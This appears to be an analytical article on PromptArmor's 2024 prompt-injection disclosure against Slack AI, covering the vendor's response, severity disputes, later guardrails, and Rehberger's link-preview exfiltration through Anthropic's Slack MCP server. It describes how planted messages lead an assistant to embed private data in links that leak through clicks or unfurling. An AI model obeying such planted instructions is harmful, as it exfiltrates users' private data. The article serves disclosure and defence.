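PromptArmor reported the flaw to Slack on Wednesday 14 August 2024, the day Slack AI began to search files. On Thursday Slack asked for more information. PromptArmor sent more videos and screenshots, and said it would publish because the flaw was severe and Slack AI now searched files. On Friday Slack asked another question, which PromptArmor answered the same day. On Monday 19 August Slack replied that it had reviewed the report and found the evidence insufficient. PromptArmor published on Tuesday, and Slack announced a fix on Wednesday.

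Slack says it deployed the patch on Tuesday 20 August, the day PromptArmor published its findings. SC Media said Wednesday, probably confusing the patch with its announcement, since the statement it received from Salesforce gave no date. If Slack's date is right, it deployed the patch about a day after finding the evidence insufficient. PromptArmor's publication is the obvious explanation, though Slack has never said what changed its mind.

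Slack's public statement left out the private correspondence. It began with the blog post of 20 August and said Slack opened an investigation "when we became aware of the report". A customer who read only this would conclude that Slack had learned of the problem and fixed it that day. Slack did not name PromptArmor, and Salesforce did not directly confirm to SC Media that the two companies were describing the same issue.

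### The "intended behavior" reply

PromptArmor quoted Slack's reason for rejecting the report. Slack wrote that the information PromptArmor requested from Slack AI in the first video was in a public channel, #slackaitesting2. Slack said this was "intended behavior" because any member of a workspace can search public channels without joining them.

Slack's reply did not address PromptArmor's complaint, which was that a message in a public channel could make Slack AI reveal information from a private one. Slack was right that Slack AI was supposed to search public channels, and PromptArmor agreed.

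It is unclear what the first video showed. It may have been a version of the phishing demonstration, in which the citation did lead to the attacker's public channel and no private data was at stake. Or the reviewer may have misread the planted message, which opened with "EldritchNexus API key:" and could look like someone posting the key in public. In either case, the reviewer seems to have relied on Slack AI's citation to work out where the answer had come from, writing "as shown in the reference", even though the citations were unreliable. The passage PromptArmor quoted covers only the first of the several videos it had sent.

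Willison concluded from the reply that Slack did "not yet understand the nature and severity of this problem". He wrote this on 20 August, before Slack announced its patch, but it is a fair reading of what Slack had said. PromptArmor was kinder, praising the security team for responding promptly and trying to understand the problem. It also noted that prompt injection was new and that much of the industry misunderstood it. This was generous, since researchers had described such attacks before Slack AI went on sale.

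### Two accounts of the severity

PromptArmor claimed that an attacker could "steal anything a user puts in a private Slack channel". Slack said that someone with an existing account in the workspace could "phish users for certain data" under "very limited and specific circumstances".

PromptArmor's claim is too strong, because the attack worked only if the victim asked a question and clicked a link. Slack was also right to mention that the attacker needed an account.

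However, "phish" is a misleading word for the API key demonstration, because the victim typed nothing. Slack told ITPro that the attacker could trick a colleague "into sharing sensitive data by crafting a phishing link", but the attacker wrote only a template for the link and did not know the key. Neither of Slack's statements mentioned private channels, the part of the report most likely to worry customers.

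Slack did not rate the flaw's severity in its statement. The current rules of its bug bounty, which pays researchers for reporting flaws, offer a rough comparison, though they may differ from those of August 2024. Slack may rate a flaw as critical if it exposes customer data without any action by the user. A high rating covers unauthorised access to sensitive data that takes more skill or context, and a medium rating covers flaws that need "significant user interaction". Under these rules, PromptArmor's attack would rate as high or medium, depending on whether one click is significant. High seems the better fit, since the victim only had to use the search tool and click a link in its answer.

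There is no public evidence that anyone used the attack to steal data. On 21 August Slack said it had no evidence "at this time" of unauthorised access to customer data, and it told ITPro it would notify affected parties if it found any. The OECD's incident monitor classes the case as a plausible future harm in an AI-generated entry titled *Slack AI Vulnerability Exposes Private Channel Data*.

Slack's assurance is some evidence, but it came only a day after publication, and Slack did not describe what it had checked. Slack could have searched for planted messages, but it does not store Slack AI's past answers, so it could not have searched them for malicious links.

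Slack also did not explain how the patch worked. It promised ITPro that attackers could not exploit "this issue", which is narrower than promising protection against prompt injection. A fix that took about a day seems more likely to have changed how Slack AI displays links than how the LLM interprets messages, but that is a guess. Slack did not say whether the patch covered instructions hidden in files, the new attack route that had made PromptArmor want to publish quickly.

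### Publication after six days

PromptArmor published the full text of its planted message, so anyone with an account in a workspace that used Slack AI could have copied it until Slack's patch took effect. PromptArmor justified publishing it by saying that customers needed to know in time to change their settings, since the file feature had substantially increased the risk and companies keep a lot of confidential data in Slack.

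This justification is only partly convincing. PromptArmor recommended a setting that stopped Slack AI from using files. That would have blocked the attack through files, which PromptArmor had not tested, but not the attack through messages in public channels, which it had shown to work. To protect against the latter, a customer would have had to stop using AI search or warn employees about its links. PromptArmor also sold AI monitoring, so it had a commercial interest in publicity.

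Slack's current bug-bounty rules give the company up to 30 days to consider a report and require researchers to get its approval before publishing anywhere. PromptArmor has not said whether it reported through that programme, but Slack had considered and rejected the report by the time PromptArmor published. Waiting longer would have made sense if Slack had still been investigating, or if PromptArmor thought explaining again would work. The notice on the second day is harder to defend, because Slack had barely begun to ask questions. Still, Slack patched the flaw on the day PromptArmor published, although it had seen no need to the day before.

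### The guardrails in 2026

In its *Guide to the Slack AI Guardrails*, Slack now lists six protections for its AI features, in addition to the safety measures built into the LLMs. If a request or an answer fails a check, Slack may block or modify it. The guide does not give the date Slack added each protection, so it is unclear which, if any, was the August 2024 patch.

Slack describes most of the guardrails in a single phrase. The table's entries on what they might have done in the API key demonstration are therefore inferences from their names and from how the attack worked.

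| Guardrail | Where it would probably act | Possible effect on the attack |
|---|---|---|
| Content safety filters | The user's question | Little, since the victim asked an innocent question |
| Content thresholds against hallucination | The choice of material for an answer | Little, since the planted message matched the question closely |
| Context engineering | The assembly of the context window | Could separate or label colleagues' messages so that the LLM is less likely to obey them |
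| Explicit safety instructions | The LLM's processing of the context window | Could lead the LLM to ignore the planted instruction |
| Output format validation | The finished answer | Could reject an error notice where Slack expects an answer with citations |
| URL filtering | Links in the finished answer | Could remove the link before the victim sees it |

The content safety filters sound the most relevant, because Slack says they detect prompt injection. But Slack's *Securing the Agentic Enterprise* (2025) says they "analyze user queries", and Slack's AI principles add that they do this before the queries reach Slackbot or the search tool. That helps when the user is the attacker, but PromptArmor's attacker never queried Slack AI. To catch the attack, the filters would also have had to examine the retrieved messages, and Slack does not say they do.

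Administrators can set these filters to Maximum, Default or None. Default is meant to block prompt attacks along with violent, hateful, sexual and illegal content. Maximum also blocks targeted profiling of employees, such as questions about their performance, so it offers no obvious extra protection against a planted message. None turns off the filters but leaves the other guardrails in place.

Context engineering addresses the right part of the attack, when an attacker's message and a private one end up in the same context window. Slack does not explain how its context engineering works and claims only that it reduces the risk. David C expects such measures to do no more than that.

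URL filtering is more promising because it can work even after the LLM has obeyed the attacker. Its value depends on the rule Slack uses, and three rules are plausible:

- **Block known phishing sites.** This would miss a site that the attacker had just registered.
- **Allow only addresses that appear word for word in the retrieved messages.** This would stop the API key attack, because nobody had posted the address that contained the real key. It would not stop the phishing demonstration if the LLM simply copied the attacker's link.
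- **Allow only approved sites.** This would stop both attacks, as long as no attacker controlled an approved site, but it would also remove many ordinary links that colleagues share.

In a 2026 post about connecting Slackbot to other companies' tools, Slack refers to "special handling for AI-generated URLs", which does not settle the question. *Slack AI Agent Security Risks*, an assessment by the security vendor Adversa AI, describes the filter as blocking "known-bad patterns". That would be the weakest of the three rules, but the Slack pages it cites do not describe the filter that way.

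No public test shows how well these defences work. Adversa AI calls their effectiveness since the patch "not independently verified". It scored the product from Slack's documentation and PromptArmor's report, and its page gives two different overall scores, so its scores deserve little weight. Salesforce does commission security tests. Its *Vulnerability/Penetration Report Summary* (2026) attests to one in August 2026 on the Slack Agentforce application, a related product, but Salesforce deliberately left out the findings.

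### Slackbot

Researchers do not appear to have published a successful prompt-injection attack on Slackbot in 2025 or 2026. The closest finding concerns Einstein, another Salesforce AI product. SecurityWeek reported that researchers at the security firm Zenity planted malicious customer-service cases that hijacked Einstein when it processed them. The researchers showed how an attacker could change the email addresses on all of a company's cases and so redirect its correspondence with customers.

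The lack of findings is weak evidence that Slackbot is safe. On 15 August 2025, Slack paused all disclosure through HackerOne, the platform that hosts its bug bounty. Researchers who report a flaw through the programme break its rules if they then describe it on a blog or at a conference without Slack's approval, even if Slack has already fixed it. Someone may therefore have found a flaw in Slackbot, and Slack may have fixed it, without customers hearing about it.

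Slackbot also takes in more material than the 2024 search tool did. It can connect to outside services through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard for linking AI agents to tools and data. According to Slack, an administrator must approve each connection. In the first release, Slackbot can only read from these services, and Slack says the user will have to confirm each action once Slackbot can write or delete. Confirmation should make it harder for a planted instruction to change records unnoticed, but read-only access can still bring an outsider's text into the context window.

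Investigators would have an easier time now than in 2024. Slack says it now logs AI actions and lets security teams export conversations with Slackbot. They can also export the questions from ordinary AI search, but Slack still does not store the answers, where a malicious link would appear.

### Link previews and attacks without a click

PromptArmor's attack required the victim to click a link. On 21 August 2024, the day of Slack's statement, Willison drew attention to a route he had not thought of before, which needs no click. It relies on link previews, also called unfurling. When someone posts a link in Slack, Slack's servers request the page to show its title and image. If an AI agent posts a link with a secret in the address, that request sends the secret to whoever owns the site.

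Willison was passing on work by the security researcher Johann Rehberger, who quoted Slack's documentation to show that Slack previewed links from apps by default, as it did links from people. Rehberger also explained that developers whose apps post to Slack can stop it from requesting the linked page by setting two options, `unfurl_links` and `unfurl_media`, to false.

The following year Rehberger found that Anthropic had not done this in its Slack MCP server, a connector that lets AI agents read and post messages in Slack. *Security Advisory* (2025), published on his blog Embrace The Red, describes how he asked Anthropic's Claude Desktop app to summarise a document and post the summary for his team. The document contained an instruction to include a link whose address ended with the latest message from another channel. Claude posted the link to a private channel, and when Slack requested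 the address to generate a preview, it sent the message to Rehberger's server.

An administrator could have restricted the connector to that one private channel and reasonably assumed that nothing would leave the company. The restriction would have worked as intended, since Claude posted only where it had permission, but the data leaked through Slack's preview of the link.

Rehberger reported the problem to Anthropic on 27 May 2025. Anthropic archived the connector two days later, possibly for unrelated reasons, and did not plan to patch it, although people were still downloading it more than 14,000 times a week. The flaw is now listed as CVE-2025-34072 in the public catalogue of software vulnerabilities. The security company VulnCheck rated its severity 9.3 out of 10, while Rehberger rated it 7.5. NVD's *CVE-2025-34072 Detail* (2025), the entry in the US government's vulnerability database,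 includes no score from NVD itself.

VulnCheck's 9.3 score is based on the assumption that the attack requires nothing from the user, which is reasonable for an agent running unattended. But Rehberger observed that most AI apps ask for permission before using a tool, unless the user has turned these requests off, so 9.3 is probably too high for many users.

PromptArmor published a follow-up, *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps*, in February 2026. It found that OpenClaw, an AI agent that people can message through apps such as Slack and Telegram, was exposed by default on Telegram. PromptArmor also set up a website where anyone could test whether their own combination of agent and app leaked data through previews. Participants chose what to test and report, so the results can identify risky combinations but not how common they are.

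These findings concern other companies' agents, not Slack AI. In the Slack cases, Slack's part was to fetch the link preview. This is easy to get wrong because some of Slack's preview software identifies itself to websites as "Slackbot", which is also the name of Slack's assistant. A "Slackbot" entry in an attacker's log shows that Slack previewed a link, not that the assistant wrote the link.

PromptArmor wants messaging companies to consider letting customers control previews for individual chats and channels. A customer could then turn previews off wherever it uses an agent, without relying on each agent's developer to set the right options.
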